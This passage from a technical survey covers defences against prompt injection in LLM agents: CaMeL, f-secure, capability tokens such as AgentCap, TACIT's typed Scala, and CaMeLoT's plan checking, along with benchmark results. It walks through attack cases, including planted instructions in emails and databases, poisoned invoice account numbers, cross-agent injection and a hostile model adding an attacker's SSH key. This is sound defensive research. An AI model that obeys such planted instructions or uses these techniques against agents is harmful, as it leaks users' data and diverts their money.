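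Under this definition, untrusted data may still determine which of the plan's existing branches runs. Suppose a plan says to email the manager if any budget exceeds $1,000. An attacker who submits a false budget can trigger that email, but cannot make the agent email anyone else. Foerster and colleagues use the term "branch steering" for deliberately manipulating data to control which branch runs. It is a bigger problem for agents that operate a screen.

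The data passed to each call needs separate protection. Costa et al. describe a user who asks an agent to summarise three emails and send the summary to a colleague. One email contains an instruction for the quarantined model to return an empty summary. The agent reads the emails, has them summarised and messages the right colleague as planned, but the message is empty. A false summary would probably be worse, because the colleague might act on it.

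A policy that requires trusted arguments would block the poisoned summary, but it would also block every accurate summary of an outsider's email, because the labels record only that an outsider could have influenced the text, not whether it is accurate.

Attacks on data don't need a hidden instruction. Girrens and Wang describe an invoice that lists the attacker's bank account. The agent fetches the invoice, extracts the account number and pays the attacker, even though its plan is correct. *Right Tool, Wrong Parameters* (2026) calls such attacks parameter poisoning and reports that they succeeded 93% of the time against agents without a defence.

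The quarantined model can also leak secrets through its answers. In *On the Relative Security of Prompt Injection*, Dongol (2026) analyses the dual-LLM pattern by assuming that the attacker controls the quarantined model's answer and can base it on anything the planner passed to that model. If the planner passed it both an attacker's email and Alice's calendar, a drafted reply could contain the whole calendar. In *Design Patterns for Securing LLM Agents against Prompt Injections*, Beurer-Kellner, Buesser and colleagues (2025) warn that such a reply could hide the data in non-printing characters, which even a careful user would miss. If the data is labelled, the draft inherits the calendar's restrictions on who may read it, so a policy can block the reply without anyone finding the hidden text.

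Control-flow integrity may give very little protection if the plan leaves the arguments open. Beurer-Kellner and colleagues consider a file assistant that commits in advance to using only the commands for finding and moving files. An injection could still make it find sensitive files and move them to a public network drive.

This distinction explains why two assessments appear to conflict. Foerster and colleagues write that the dual-LLM split guarantees control-flow integrity but does not prevent attacks on data. *Securing LLM Agents Need Intent-to-Execution Integrity* (2026) rates CaMeL as fully enforcing the integrity of both control flow and data. That rating includes CaMeL's policies and information-flow tracking, whereas Foerster and colleagues deliberately ran CaMeL and FIDES without their policies. The higher rating is fair only if someone has written policies that cover the tool-call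 arguments that matter.

### How much the planner may see

An earlier system, f-secure, described in *System-Level Defense against Indirect Prompt Injection Attacks* (Wu, Cecchetti and Xiao, 2024), shows its planner more than CaMeL does but checks less. The planner reads trusted results in full, while a security monitor withholds untrusted ones. For each withheld result, the planner sees a reference such as `{Data_output:1}`, which it can pass to a later step.

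The monitor checks each item separately. In one example, a user wants the agent to read emails about company budgets and notify the manager if any budget exceeds $1,000. The search returns two emails from trusted colleagues and one from an attacker. The planner reads the colleagues' emails and decides what to do, and the attacker's email never reaches the planner.

Wu and colleagues call the resulting property execution trace non-compromise. Let q be the user's request, π a sequence of steps, and Q₁ and Q₂ two collections of data that differ only in their untrusted parts. Then

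Pr[π | q, Q₁] = Pr[π | q, Q₂]

so untrusted data cannot change even the probability that the agent takes a given sequence of steps. This is stricter than the control-flow integrity of Peters-Gill and colleagues, because untrusted data cannot select a branch either. The false budget that triggers an email in a CaMeL program would have no effect on the plan in f-secure, but neither would a genuine budget from an unknown sender.

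According to Girrens and Wang, f-secure does not check the integrity of every call's arguments. If the planner passes a reference to Bob's address, the executor will use whatever address the notes contain. The planner's safety also depends on accurate labels. If the software labels an email as trusted because a colleague sent it, but the colleague has pasted in an attacker's text, that text reaches the planner.

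Beurer-Kellner and colleagues set out six design patterns in 2025, built on the principle that once an agent has read untrusted input, that input must be unable to trigger a consequential action. Five of them differ mainly in what the model that chooses the tool calls may see:

| Design | What that model sees | What untrusted data can still change |
|---|---|---|
| Action-selector | the request, but no tool results | none of the agent's choices |
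| Code-then-execute (CaMeL) | the request, before any tool runs | values, and the choice between planned branches |
| Dual LLM | names of variables | the contents of the variables |
| Map-reduce | a restricted answer about each document | how the agent treats that document |
| f-secure | trusted results, and references to the rest | the data that steps pass on |
| FIDES | trusted results, names of variables, and anything it opens | arguments, and later calls once it opens a variable, within the policy |
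| Plan-then-execute | all results, but only after it has fixed the list of calls | the arguments of those calls |

An action-selector matches each request to one of a set of predefined actions. A customer-service bot, for example, might either fetch a link to the customer's last order or point them to the password settings. The selector never reads what its actions return, so text planted in those results cannot reach it.

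Map-reduce is useful when an agent must process many documents. Suppose a user wants this month's invoices sent to the accounting department. A separate quarantined model reads each file and outputs only whether it is an invoice, and another component collects the matching files and sends them. An attacker can get a malicious file included, but that file cannot affect how the agent treats the others. Beurer-Kellner and colleagues point out that the attacker could have done the same by planting a real invoice.

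The sixth pattern, context-minimization, deals with hostile text in the user's own prompt. Suppose a customer asks a sales chatbot for a quote on a car and adds instructions meant to win a large discount. The software has the model turn the request into a database query and then deletes the customer's prompt, so the instructions cannot influence how the model presents the price.

### Untrusted text that returns as an instruction

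In most of these designs, the planner trusts whatever arrives as the user's request. Willison warned in 2023 that the dual-LLM pattern fails if someone tricks the user into pasting hostile text into the chat. Hostile text can also reach the planner without the user's involvement when the planner takes its instructions from another agent.

Peters-Gill and colleagues demonstrated this with three CaMeL agents. A coordinating agent could call one agent that searched a database and another that sent messages. The user asked for a summary of all job applicants to be sent to Julie on Slack, a workplace chat service. The database contained a planted instruction to send the data to an outside email address.

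The coordinating agent and the database agent kept the planted line in variables, so their programs did not change. But the coordinating agent's program inserted the summary into its request to the messaging agent, which treated the request as its user's instructions. The messaging agent's planner read the planted line and wrote a program that sent the applicants' details to the attacker as well as to Julie. The system had lost control-flow integrity even though each agent had followed its own plan.

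The proposed remedy, multi-CaMeL, sends instructions and untrusted data between agents through separate channels and keeps the labels attached to the data. The receiving planner reads only the instructions. In tests without any security policies, attacks succeeded 12.9% of the time without CaMeL, 0.2% with separate CaMeL agents and never with multi-CaMeL. The small gap between the last two suggests that few of the benchmark's attacks crossed from one agent to another. An attacker who knew about the weakness would probably succeed more often against the separate agents.

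Stored data can cause the same failure later. In an example from Girrens and Wang, a user has an agent save the details of an invoice on Monday, then tells it on Tuesday to pay "the invoice we discussed yesterday". If the software shows the saved text to the planner on Tuesday, an instruction hidden in the invoice reaches the planner too.

The SPA system instead gives the later planner only a description of each saved item. When the software carries out the plan, it retrieves the item itself with its original label. The bank account on the invoice is therefore still untrusted on Tuesday, and a policy that requires a trusted account will block the payment.

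## Capabilities and capability tokens

A planted instruction can make Alice's assistant forward her whole mailbox only if the assistant has the right to read and send all her mail. Labels and the split between planner and reader leave that right in place and control how the assistant uses it. Capability security instead gives each program only the rights its task needs.

### References and access lists

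A capability is an unforgeable reference that carries the right to use the object it refers to. According to *Early Capability Architectures*, Dennis and Van Horn of MIT introduced the word in 1966, in a design for an operating system that runs many programs at once. Each computation in their design had a list of capabilities and could use nothing outside it.

Most systems in use today rely on access lists. Each resource has its own list, which records which users may do what with it. In a table of permissions with a row for each user and a column for each file, a column is one file's access list, and a row is one user's list of capabilities.

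*Capability Myths Demolished*, by Miller, Yee and Shapiro, argues that access lists and capability systems differ, although both record the same permissions and many people have taken them to be equivalent. Under an access list, a program asks for a file by name, and the system looks up the rights of the user who started the program. The name carries no rights, and the program never chooses which of its rights to use. The paper calls this ambient authority. In a capability system, the program must present a reference that carries the right to use the resource, so it cannot name a resource without having that right.

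Miller and Shapiro, in *Paradigm Regained*, illustrate the difference with two Unix commands that copy a file:

```
cp foo.txt bar.txt
cat < foo.txt > bar.txt
```

The `cp` program receives two names as text, and it needs all the user's rights to the file system to open whatever files the user might name. In the second command, the user's shell opens both files and passes `cat` two references. Unix still runs `cat` with all the user's rights, but `cat` needs only the two references for this job. If it had only those, a malicious version could damage only `bar.txt`.

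In the object-capability model, a program gets a reference from its creator, by creating something itself, or in a message from another program. For a program Alice to pass program Bob a reference to program Carol, Alice must already hold references to both. Two groups of programs with no references between them can therefore never become connected. If Alice may need to withdraw Bob's access later, she gives him a reference to a small forwarding program instead of Carol and keeps the ability to disable the forwarder.

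### The confused deputy

*The Confused Deputy* (Hardy, 1988) describes an incident at Tymshare, a company that sold time on shared computers. Its compiler let users name a file to receive debugging output. The compiler also recorded statistics in a file in a system directory called SYSX, so Tymshare had given it the right to write anywhere in that directory, which also held the company's billing file. A user named the billing file as the destination for debugging output. The operating system allowed the write because the compiler had the right to write in SYSX, and the compiler overwrote the billing information.

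Hardy traces the problem to the compiler's "authority stemming from two sources", the user and Tymshare, which it could not keep apart. Checking the file name would not have helped much, because some users had good reasons to write to SYSX and the directory held other sensitive files. Tymshare added a system call that let the compiler choose which authority to use, but some applications soon needed more than two authorities. With capabilities, the compiler would hold a reference to the statistics file, and the user would pass the compiler a reference to the debugging output file. A user with no right to the billing file would have no reference to it, so could not pass one to the compiler.

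An agent that acts with all its user's rights is in the same position as the compiler. In the GitLost attack, GitHub's agent had access to private repositories, and a stranger used a public issue to instruct it on what to do with that access. Suresh and Gao (2026) point out in *AGENTCAP* that such an attack need not bypass any permission check, because it redirects an agent that already has permission. The problem grows when agents pass work to other agents. In *A Five-Plane Reference Architecture for Runtime Governance of Production AI Agents*, Tallam (2026) regards every agent that acts for a chain of delegators as a potential confused deputy.

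Hardy's remedy works less well for agents than for compilers. The compiler's code would have used each reference for its intended purpose, but a language model that holds a reference to Alice's mailbox may use it for an attacker's purpose after reading a planted instruction. Miller and colleagues acknowledge that ending ambient authority only makes confusion avoidable, since a program must still keep track of what each right is for. Dependable protection against a hijacked agent therefore comes from limiting which references it holds.

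In *On access control, capabilities, their equivalence, and confused deputy attacks*, Rajani, Garg and Rezk prove that access control and object capabilities are fundamentally different. They also formally define freedom from confused-deputy attacks and relate it to information-flow integrity, the property that Denning-style labels protect.

### Three meanings of "capability"

Papers on agents use the word for three different things:

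| Meaning | What it is | What it lets the holder do |
|---|---|---|
| Object capability | a reference that an operating system or programming language protects | use the resource, and pass the reference to programs it can already reach |
| Capability token | a signed message that an agent presents to a server | make the requests that the message permits |
| CaMeL's "capability" | a tag on a value that records its sources and permitted readers | nothing by itself, though a policy consults it before a tool call |

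An object capability is a reference that a program cannot create from ordinary data, and some languages track these references in a program's types. A capability token is ordinary data protected by a signature, so any agent that can send text can send a copy of its token. Miller and colleagues compare such tokens to keys that people can copy and hand to anyone. They argue that two common criticisms of capabilities, that nobody can stop them from spreading or revoke them, apply to such keys but not to object references. Token systems therefore need extra measures, such as tying each token to one agent.

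A CaMeL tag that lists Alice and Bob as permitted readers of a document does not give any program the right to open or email it. Suresh and Gao therefore group CaMeL with the label-based systems FIDES and RTBAS, and present their own token system as a complement to all three.

### How AgentCap issues and checks tokens

AgentCap, which Suresh and Gao published in November 2026, puts two checks between the model and its tools:

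1. The model proposes a tool call and declares an intent, such as paying a bill.
2. A policy engine, which is ordinary code, decides whether to issue a token for the call.
3. The agent presents the token to a gateway along with the call.
4. The gateway checks the token and forwards the call to the tool.

The token contains identifiers for itself, the agent and the session. It specifies the permitted action, the resource, the declared intent, the issue and expiry times, and the number of calls allowed. It also includes the agent's trust score, any permissions the agent must already hold, the combinations of permissions it must not hold, and a reference to the matching audit log entry. The policy engine signs all of this, so changing any field invalidates the signature.

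The engine issues a token only if the tool is in its catalogue, the policy permits the declared intent, the agent holds the prerequisite permissions, and the new token would not complete a forbidden combination. The gateway then checks the token's signature, expiry time, revocation status and remaining calls, and whether the agent, action and resource match the token.

Suresh and Gao's example rule for a banking agent allows one transfer within 30 seconds, only after the agent has obtained permission to check the balance, and only if the intent is to pay a bill or send a payment. A hijacked model can lie about its intent, so the rule also checks where the recipient came from. AgentCap rejects a recipient that appears only in untrusted content and accepts one that also appears in the user's request. A similar rule for email would block a message to Bob if his address appeared only in the meeting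 notes, as CaMeL's example policy does. The banking rule does not check where the amount came from, and its budget of one limits the number of transfers but not how much money is sent.

The trust score falls by 30% after each denied request or anomalous result. From the default starting score of 0.8, three anomalies lower it to 0.560, 0.392 and then 0.274, at which point AgentCap cuts the agent off. Each normal result closes 1% of the gap between the current score and 1. The payment rule requires a score of at least 0.8, so under these settings a single denial would block new payments until about 79 normal results had followed. An attacker who cannot steal money might still be able to stop the agent from paying bills.

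### A chain of delegated tokens

Attenuation means passing on a permission no stronger than the one held. In AgentCap, an agent can give another agent a child token if

a′ = a, r′ = r, b′ ≤ b, e′ ≤ e, d′ < d

Here a is the action, r the resource, b the number of calls, e the expiry time and d the number of further delegations allowed. Marked symbols are the child's values.

Suppose Alice's coordinating agent receives a token for sending calendar invitations and delegates part of the job:

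| Holder | Calls allowed | Expires | Further delegations |
|---|---|---|---|
| Coordinating agent | 10 | 10:10 | 2 |
| Scheduling agent | 6 | 10:05 | 1 |
| Reminder agent | 6 | 10:02 | 0 |

The reminder agent can have as many calls as the scheduling agent, because a delegated token can keep the same call limit. The delegation depth must decrease with each delegation, so the reminder agent cannot pass its token on. If the scheduling agent tried to give the reminder agent seven calls, an expiry time of 10:06 or the right to delete events, AgentCap would reject the token.

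When the reminder agent makes a call, the gateway works back from that agent's token to the coordinating agent's. At each step it checks the signature, the limits inherited from the parent and whether anyone has revoked the token. Revoking the coordinating agent's token at 10:01 therefore stops the other two at once.

These conditions don't limit the total number of calls. If the coordinating agent also gives a second agent six calls, each child satisfies b′ ≤ b, since 6 ≤ 10, but the two siblings can make 12 calls together. The scheduling and reminder agents could also make 12, even though they belong to a single chain. To prevent this, the gateway would have to count each child's calls against its parent's limit or cap the sum, and Suresh and Gao describe neither.

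The difficulty affects delegation in general. *Fault-Tolerant Budget Conservation in Distributed Multi-Agent Delegation* (2026) considers two child agents that hold the same narrow permission when only one unit of budget remains. Attenuation cannot determine which of them may spend it, because each token is valid by itself. *AIP* (2026), which describes a protocol for agent identity, acknowledges this limit. A 50-cent token caps only the spending made with that token, so the surrounding software has to track the total.

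*AESP* (2026), a payment protocol for agents, caps the combined spending of a parent agent's children. It reserves each child's limit out of the parent's remaining budget and also debits the parent whenever the child spends. A parent that reserves six of its ten units for one child has only four left for the next. *Bounded Agents* (2026) also has the infrastructure track limits across a whole session, including a limit on irreversible effects. Both designs need some component to keep a shared, up-to-date record, so agents can no longer delegate a budget safely without contacting that component.

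### Macaroons and tokens tied to an identity

AgentCap's attenuation draws on macaroons, a form of token that Birgisson, Politz and colleagues introduced in *Macaroons* (2014) for online services. A macaroon carries a list of conditions, called caveats, and any holder can add more. Its protection comes from HMAC, a function that computes a short fingerprint of a message with a secret key. Each fingerprint serves as the key for the next:

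s₀ = HMAC(K, identifier)

s₁ = HMAC(s₀, "chunks 100 to 500")

s₂ = HMAC(s₁, "read only")

The storage service in this example knows the secret key K. The final macaroon contains the identifier, both conditions and only the last fingerprint, s₂. Its holder cannot drop the "read only" condition, because that would require s₁, which nobody can feasibly work out from s₂. The service recomputes the whole chain from K and checks every condition against the request.

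A holder can make a weaker macaroon without contacting the service. The holder can also narrow the resource, for example from chunks 100 to 500 to just chunk 235. AgentCap's conditions cannot change the resource, so an agent with access to a folder cannot delegate access to just one file in it. A macaroon caveat can also require proof from an outside service, such as approval from an abuse-detection system.

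Macaroons have two weaknesses here. Only the service that holds K can verify them, whereas anyone with the policy engine's public key can verify the signature on an AgentCap token. A macaroon also works for whoever holds it unless a caveat restricts who may use it. *Delegation Without Trust* (2026) combines macaroon-style tokens with a check on the agent's identity, in a program of about 160 lines. In a small test, the program blocked four attacks that succeeded on the default software: a confused-deputy attack, a stolen token, an attempt to gain extra rights and a compromised sub-agent.

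In *Crypto-bound identity-verified capability tokens for coordinating distributed AI agents*, Subramanian and Sengupta (2026) also tie each token to an agent's identity. A service can challenge the agent to sign a random string with its private key. The key stays in a separate wallet program that the model cannot read, so an injection cannot make the model reveal it.

In their example, a user gives a coordinating agent a budget of $5,000 for a trip to Paris. The coordinator gives a flight agent permission to reserve tickets for up to $1,500, and three other agents arrange hotels, restaurants and local transport. The coordinator could give all four agents $1,500 each. Each token would be narrower than the coordinator's, but together they would allow $6,000 of spending. An airline checking the flight token could not see the hotel spending. The user might notice, because the agents can only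 hold reservations until the user approves the complete plan.

A service that checks a token without contacting anyone cannot learn that the user has withdrawn permission. Subramanian and Sengupta suggest either issuing tokens that last about five minutes or checking every parent token, which takes longer as the chain grows. They generally accept the extra delay in return for quick revocation. They propose a design but report no attack tests.

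### What the tests of AgentCap found

Suresh and Gao tested AgentCap on AgentDojo and on InjecAgent, another benchmark of prompt injections, with 2,003 attack cases in all:

| Benchmark and model | Attack success without AgentCap | Attack success with AgentCap | Drop in harmless tasks completed |
|---|---|---|---|
| AgentDojo, GPT-4o | 45.63% | 5.09% | 3.1 points |
| AgentDojo, GPT-5.4 | 33.23% | 0% | 7.2 points |
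| InjecAgent, GPT-4o | 23.24% | 8.63% | 3.9 points |
| InjecAgent, GPT-5.4 | 11.95% | 0% | 2.0 points |

Some of the attacks that still succeeded aimed only to change the agent's written answer, which no check on tool calls can prevent. In the rest, the policy left an argument unprotected or an untrusted field unlabeled. Each figure comes from a single run, and nobody adapted the attacks to AgentCap, so the zeros are weak evidence that it would stop a determined attacker.

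Suresh and Gao also wrote AgentCap's policies specifically for the test, using the tool descriptions and the benchmark's user tasks, and froze them before the runs. A real assistant receives requests that its developers did not foresee. Knowing the tasks beforehand also gave AgentCap an advantage in the comparison with Progent, whose policies GPT-4o wrote during the runs. Progent stopped about as many attacks but completed 68% of harmless tasks, compared with 78% for AgentCap.

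In a much smaller test of delegation, AgentCap rejected all nine attempts to widen a delegated permission or reuse it in an unrelated session. In another hand-built scenario, it blocked all three malicious calls, while a simpler version that limited only the tokens' lifetime and number of calls let eight calls through before reaching its call limit. Short-lived, limited permissions therefore seem to do little against a hijacked agent unless the system also checks where the arguments in its calls came from.

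### Why permissions need flow rules

Even perfectly enforced permissions can allow a leak. Suppose Alice asks her assistant to look up the next payday in the payroll file and email the date to Bob, who isn't allowed to see anyone's salary.

1. The assistant needs to read the payroll file, so it properly holds that permission.
2. It needs to email Bob, so it properly holds that one too.
3. Once it has read the file, the model has every salary in its input, and it also writes the email.
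4. The permission to email Bob covers the date and the salaries alike, because it does not depend on where the text came from.

A hijacked or mistaken model can therefore send Bob the salaries without exceeding either permission. Shorter expiry times and smaller budgets wouldn't prevent this, since one email is enough. A developer could narrow the first permission with a tool that returns only the payday, and Miller and Shapiro describe such filters. But the developer would have to foresee the question, and much of an agent's usefulness comes from handling requests nobody foresaw.

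*A Note on the Confinement Problem* (Lampson, 1973) describes the same difficulty for ordinary programs. A customer gives a service confidential data that it needs for its work. Even if the service cannot open any of the customer's other files, it can pass this data to the service's owner. It might save the data in a file, send a message or encode the data in the bill. It could also use a covert channel, one not intended for communication, for example by varying the load on the computer. The email to Bob, like the bill, is a legitimate channel that carries data it shouldn't.

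Lampson's simplest solution forbids the service from calling any other program, which he considered quite impractical. A looser rule lets it call programs that the customer trusts or that are themselves confined. The customer must then control what the service puts into any legitimate or covert channel. For Alice, that could mean an email template whose only blank is a date. Even a date could encode a little of the payroll data, and Lampson suggests limiting the capacity of such channels where closing them would take too many resources.

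Object capabilities can enforce confinement by withholding references. Miller and Shapiro compare a confined program to a pocket calculator with no wires coming out of it. A customer who starts a program and gives it no outside references knows that it cannot send the customer's data anywhere, except through covert channels, which Miller and Shapiro exclude. Willison's quarantined model, which has no tools, is confined in much the same way. Alice's assistant cannot be confined this way, because her request requires it to send something.

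AgentCap can forbid an agent from holding two permissions together, such as access to sensitive data and a route to the outside. Its analysis tool checked all 28 pairs of permissions in a customer-service policy and found that the policy allowed no pair combining such access with such a route. A ban like this prevents the leak but also blocks Alice's task. Dividing the permissions between two agents doesn't help if the agents can communicate, because the one that reads the payroll can send its contents to the other. Miller and Shapiro describe this as the difference between permission, which is what a program may do directly, and authority, which includes what it can bring about through others.

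A flow rule can permit the email while restricting its contents. *DelegateGuard* (2026) builds such rules into the permissions. Each grant lists the labels of the data an agent may handle and the sinks, or destinations, where it may send that data. A child grant's labels, operations and sinks must fall within the parent's. In one example, an agent may summarise confidential contracts for the user and internal recipients. If it tries to give a formatting agent an external web address as an additional sink, the system rejects the grant before the formatting agent starts.

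A grant for the payroll file could list Alice as its only sink. The assistant could then answer her questions about salaries and still send Bob unrelated messages, as long as the system tracked which text came from the file. The payday email would stay blocked until Alice or a policy declassified the date.

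## Checking an agent's program before it runs

A policy check that runs during a task can block a bad tool call, but it cannot undo earlier calls. If an agent writes its actions as a program, software can check the whole program before any of it runs. *Toward Safe LLM Agents*, a 2026 survey, calls such advance checks "verification" and blocking actions during a run "enforcement".

*LACUNA* (Zhao, Xu and colleagues, 2026) gives an example of why it helps to check a whole program before running it. A program requests code from a model to subtract 50 from a balance of 100 and return the new balance. The model's code subtracts the 50 but returns a sentence instead of a number. The compiler, which checks code and translates it into a runnable form, rejects all of the code before any of it runs, so the balance is still 100 and the model can try again. If the software had run the code line by line,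 the balance would already have been 50 when the error appeared, and a second attempt could have reduced it to 0. On BrowseComp-Plus, a benchmark of research questions, LACUNA rejected 8.6% of the model's code before it ran.

An advance check also covers every branch of a program, including those a runtime check misses because they don't run. But it can't use facts that are available only during the run, such as who can currently open a shared file. Two recent systems check programs in advance. TACIT checks which permissions each piece of code can use, and CaMeLoT checks the order of tool calls and where their arguments come from.

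### TACIT: permissions written into types

Odersky, Zhao and colleagues at EPFL describe TACIT in *Tracking Capabilities for Safer Agents*. The agent writes short programs in Scala, and TACIT runs only those that compile.

A type normally tells the compiler what kind of value it is dealing with, such as a number or a piece of text. An experimental Scala feature called capture checking adds a capture set, which lists the permissions that the value can use. These permissions are object capabilities, the unforgeable references described earlier. If `f` is a permission to use a file, two functions might have these types:

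- `String -> Int` takes text, returns a number and can use no permissions.
- `String ->{f} Unit` takes text, can use the file `f` and returns nothing.

The compiler works out each set from the code, so a function that uses `f` cannot leave it out of its type. Where a program expects a function with certain permissions, the compiler accepts only functions that satisfy

permissions the function can use ⊆ permissions allowed there

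A function with an empty set is called pure. It cannot write to a file, contact a network, print anything or change a variable outside itself.

TACIT uses pure functions to protect secrets. When the agent's code reads a file that an administrator has marked as classified, it gets the contents in a wrapper called `Classified`, which it cannot open. The code can pass a function to the wrapper's `map` method, which accepts only pure functions, and `map` applies the function to the contents and wraps the result again.

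The compiler accepts this program, which removes stray spaces from a secret key and saves the result in another classified file:

```
requestFileSystem("/project") {
  val key = readClassified("secrets/github.txt")
  val clean = key.map(k => k.trim)
  writeClassified("secrets/github-clean.txt", clean)
}
```

It rejects this one, which is close to code that an agent wrote in TACIT's tests:

```
requestFileSystem("/project") {
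  val key = readClassified("secrets/github.txt")
  key.map(k => println(s"GitHub API key: $k"))
}
```

Printed text goes back to the agent's model, so `println` requires an output permission, here called `io`. The function therefore has the type `String ->{io} Unit`, but `map` requires `String -> Unit`, whose permission set is empty. Since `{io}` is not contained in the empty set, the program does not compile.

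The compiler would also reject a function that only printed "done", because it does not check whether the printed text is sensitive or why the agent wants to print it. This strictness also prevents implicit flows like the one in Denning's example, because a function passed to `map` cannot change a variable defined outside it.

Permissions also end with the block of code that receives them. `requestFileSystem` grants access to one folder for the length of its block, but code might try to keep that access by returning a function that uses it:

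```
val later = requestFileSystem("/data") { fs =>
  () => fs.access("notes.txt").read()
}
```

The type of `later` would have to list `fs`, which does not exist outside the block, so `later` has no valid type and the compiler rejects the program. A TACIT permission expires at a set point in the program, rather than at a set time as an AgentCap token does.

An agent often needs to understand a secret document as well as copy or trim it. TACIT therefore offers a second model, which can run on the user's computer. It takes classified text and returns classified text, such as a summary. If the agent prints the summary, its own model receives only `Classified(****)`, while the user sees the real text through a separate channel. The summary stays in the `Classified` wrapper in later turns, so even its length remains hidden from the agent.

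This resembles Willison's dual-LLM pattern with the trust reversed. In TACIT, the model that plans is untrusted and the model that reads secrets is trusted, because TACIT is meant to stop the planning model from leaking those secrets.

### What TACIT distrusts and what it trusts

TACIT's threat model assumes that the cloud-hosted model behind the agent may be hostile and may even collude fully with the attacker. It also treats the agent's setup, all the code it submits, and any text from files, websites or tools as untrusted. TACIT therefore assumes a much stronger attacker than CaMeL or FIDES, which trust a planner that has read only trusted text.

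The trusted base still contains several components:

- the Scala compiler, including capture checking and "safe mode", which bans language features that could hide a permission
- TACIT's library, which contains the tools the agent may call, and any other code that a developer has marked as safe by hand
- the software that runs the compiled program
- the second model, if the agent uses one on classified text

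The protection also depends on how the system is set up. The documentation for lampepfl's *TACIT* recommends disabling the agent's built-in tools for files, commands and web pages, because an agent that kept them could act without submitting any code to the compiler. It also describes safe mode as experimental. At that stage, a separate validator enforced the restrictions by searching the code for forbidden patterns, which is probably easier to evade than a check inside the compiler.

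A later version of the documentation, Glama's *TACIT*, warns that the wrapper protects "confidentiality, not integrity". Agent code can wrap any text and write it over a classified file. One such file, `.ssh/authorized_keys`, lists the keys that allow someone to log in to a computer. A hostile model could add an attacker's key without reading any secrets, and the attacker could then log in and read all the secrets. Administrators can prevent this by turning off writes to classified files, but the default setting allows them.

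The same version lets programs send classified text to approved websites, for example to log in with a secret password, so the list of approved sites is part of the secrecy policy. If the list includes a site where anyone can publish, a hostile model could presumably post a secret there and read it back as ordinary text.

Odersky and colleagues exclude some other leaks from their guarantee. For example, a function could run longer when a secret bit is 1, and an observer could learn the bit from the delay. The compiler also can't check outside programs that the agent starts, so an administrator has to restrict which commands the agent can run.

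### TACIT's tests

To test for leaks, Odersky and colleagues gave agents a software project with a folder of passwords, keys and confidential documents. They combined 12 ordinary tasks with 10 prompt injections, which made 120 trials. In another 11 trials, the user asked for the secrets directly or posed as someone entitled to them. They ran all 131 trials with and without the `Classified` wrapper:

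| Model | Trials with a leak, no wrapper | Trials with a leak, wrapper | Ordinary tasks completed, no wrapper | Ordinary tasks completed, wrapper |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| Claude Sonnet 4.6 | 2 | 0 | 83.3% | 99.2% |
| MiniMax M2.5 | 11 | 0 | 88.3% | 90.0% |

The injections were a weak test, because only 3 of the 240 unprotected injection trials leaked anything. The other ten leaks came from users' own requests. The best reason to expect TACIT to stop a stronger attack is therefore the compiler's rule, which does not depend on how persuasive the attack is. Sonnet's higher completion rate with the wrapper may be a result of the setup, since Sonnet often ran out of time or stopped to warn the user about an injection.

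Writing Scala did not make agents noticeably worse at their work. On τ²-bench, a benchmark of simulated customer service, all three models did slightly better with TACIT than with ordinary tool calls:

| Model | Airline, ordinary calls | Airline, TACIT | Retail, ordinary calls | Retail, TACIT |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| gpt-oss-120b | 43.8% | 45.2% | 53.3% | 57.0% |
| MiniMax M2.5 | 58.4% | 61.0% | 75.1% | 77.5% |
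| DeepSeek V3.2 | 57.8% | 58.6% | 74.6% | 75.5% |

On SWE-bench Lite, a set of 300 real software bugs, MiniMax M2.5 fixed 41.7% with TACIT and 43.3% without it. The customer-service tools in τ²-bench returned their data unwrapped, so that benchmark measures how writing typed code affects performance, but not how hiding data from the model affects it.

AgentDojo gives a better idea of that second cost, because much of the data there was classified. The table compares the tasks completed under TACIT with the published results for CaMeL:

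| AgentDojo tasks | CaMeL, Gemini 2.5 Pro | TACIT, Gemini 2.5 Pro | CaMeL, o4-mini-high | TACIT, o4-mini-high |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| Banking | 52.8% | 56.9% | 62.5% | 59.0% |
| Office | 53.8% | 50.5% | 81.4% | 52.9% |
| Chat | 48.6% | 40.0% | 68.6% | 47.6% |
| Travel | 1.4% | 64.3% | 74.3% | 68.6% |

With o4-mini-high, TACIT did worse than the other system on all four sets of tasks and trailed by 28.5 points on office work, though Odersky and colleagues call the two systems comparable. In 1,926 trials across the two models, one attack succeeded against TACIT. The agent booked the right hotel but quoted a planted review that recommended another, and the policy allowed it to quote the review.

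The AgentDojo version also seems to have relaxed the rule about pure functions. Its tools for sending money and email did not require a tracked permission, and the model's instructions stated that side effects inside `map` would run immediately. An agent needs some exception like this to pay the amount on a classified bill. The results are therefore mainly evidence that hiding text from the model stops injections, much as in the dual-LLM pattern.

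### CaMeLoT: rules about the whole plan

TACIT's types control what code can do with a secret, but they do not by themselves require the agent to take steps in a certain order or to finish a procedure. Nikolaou and colleagues published CaMeLoT in September 2026 to check such requirements in CaMeL programs. It works between CaMeL's planner and its interpreter:

1. The planner writes a program from the user's request.
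2. CaMeLoT converts the program into a finite-state machine, which is a map of the points the program can reach and the possible moves between them.
3. It marks each point with the tool that runs there, the tools that have already run, and whether each argument is trusted. An argument counts as untrusted if CaMeLoT cannot settle its source in advance.
4. A model checker, which is a program that examines every path through such a map, compares the paths with a set of rules.
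5. If every path satisfies the rules, CaMeL runs the program under its usual runtime policies. Otherwise, the model checker returns a counterexample, meaning a path that breaks a rule. CaMeLoT describes it to the planner, which rewrites the program.

Suppose an agent handles security alerts for a company, and its plan isolates an infected computer from the network without asking anyone. The checker's counterexample would list the steps up to the isolation, none of which requests approval. The planner could then add an approval request. No tool has run yet, so this feedback contains no tool results that could carry a prompt injection.

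The rules use temporal logic, which describes how events may follow one another. Two examples from the tests, slightly simplified, are

AG(isolate computer ⇒ approval already requested)

AG(open ticket ⇒ AF(resolve or escalate ticket))

Here A means "on every path", G means "at every point" and F means "at some point from now on".

The approval rule is a safety rule, which requires that something bad never happens. Any run that breaks it does so at a particular step, so a runtime monitor that records earlier calls could block that step. The ticket rule is a liveness rule, which requires that something good eventually happens. A monitor cannot detect a violation during the run, because the agent might still close the ticket in the next step. Once the run ends, the monitor can only report the failure. A checker that has the whole plan can detect before the run that no later step closes the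 ticket.

The approval rule requires only that the agent has requested approval. CaMeLoT does not model what tools return, so it cannot check whether the security team granted it. The approval tool itself would have to stop the program after a refusal.

A program might loop over a list of any length, but the model checker needs a finite map. CaMeLoT therefore ignores the list's length and maps the loop as able to repeat or end after each pass. It also ignores branch conditions and treats both sides of each branch as possible. This is called over-approximation, because the map contains every path the real program could take and some it could not.

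CaMeLoT therefore does not miss a path that breaks a safety rule just because the path needs an unusual number of repetitions. But it can also raise false alarms. Suppose a plan requests approval if an alert is serious, and later isolates the computer if the same alert is serious. The real program never isolates the computer without requesting approval, but the map includes a path that skips the request and still isolates the computer, so CaMeLoT would reject the plan.

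### CaMeLoT's tests

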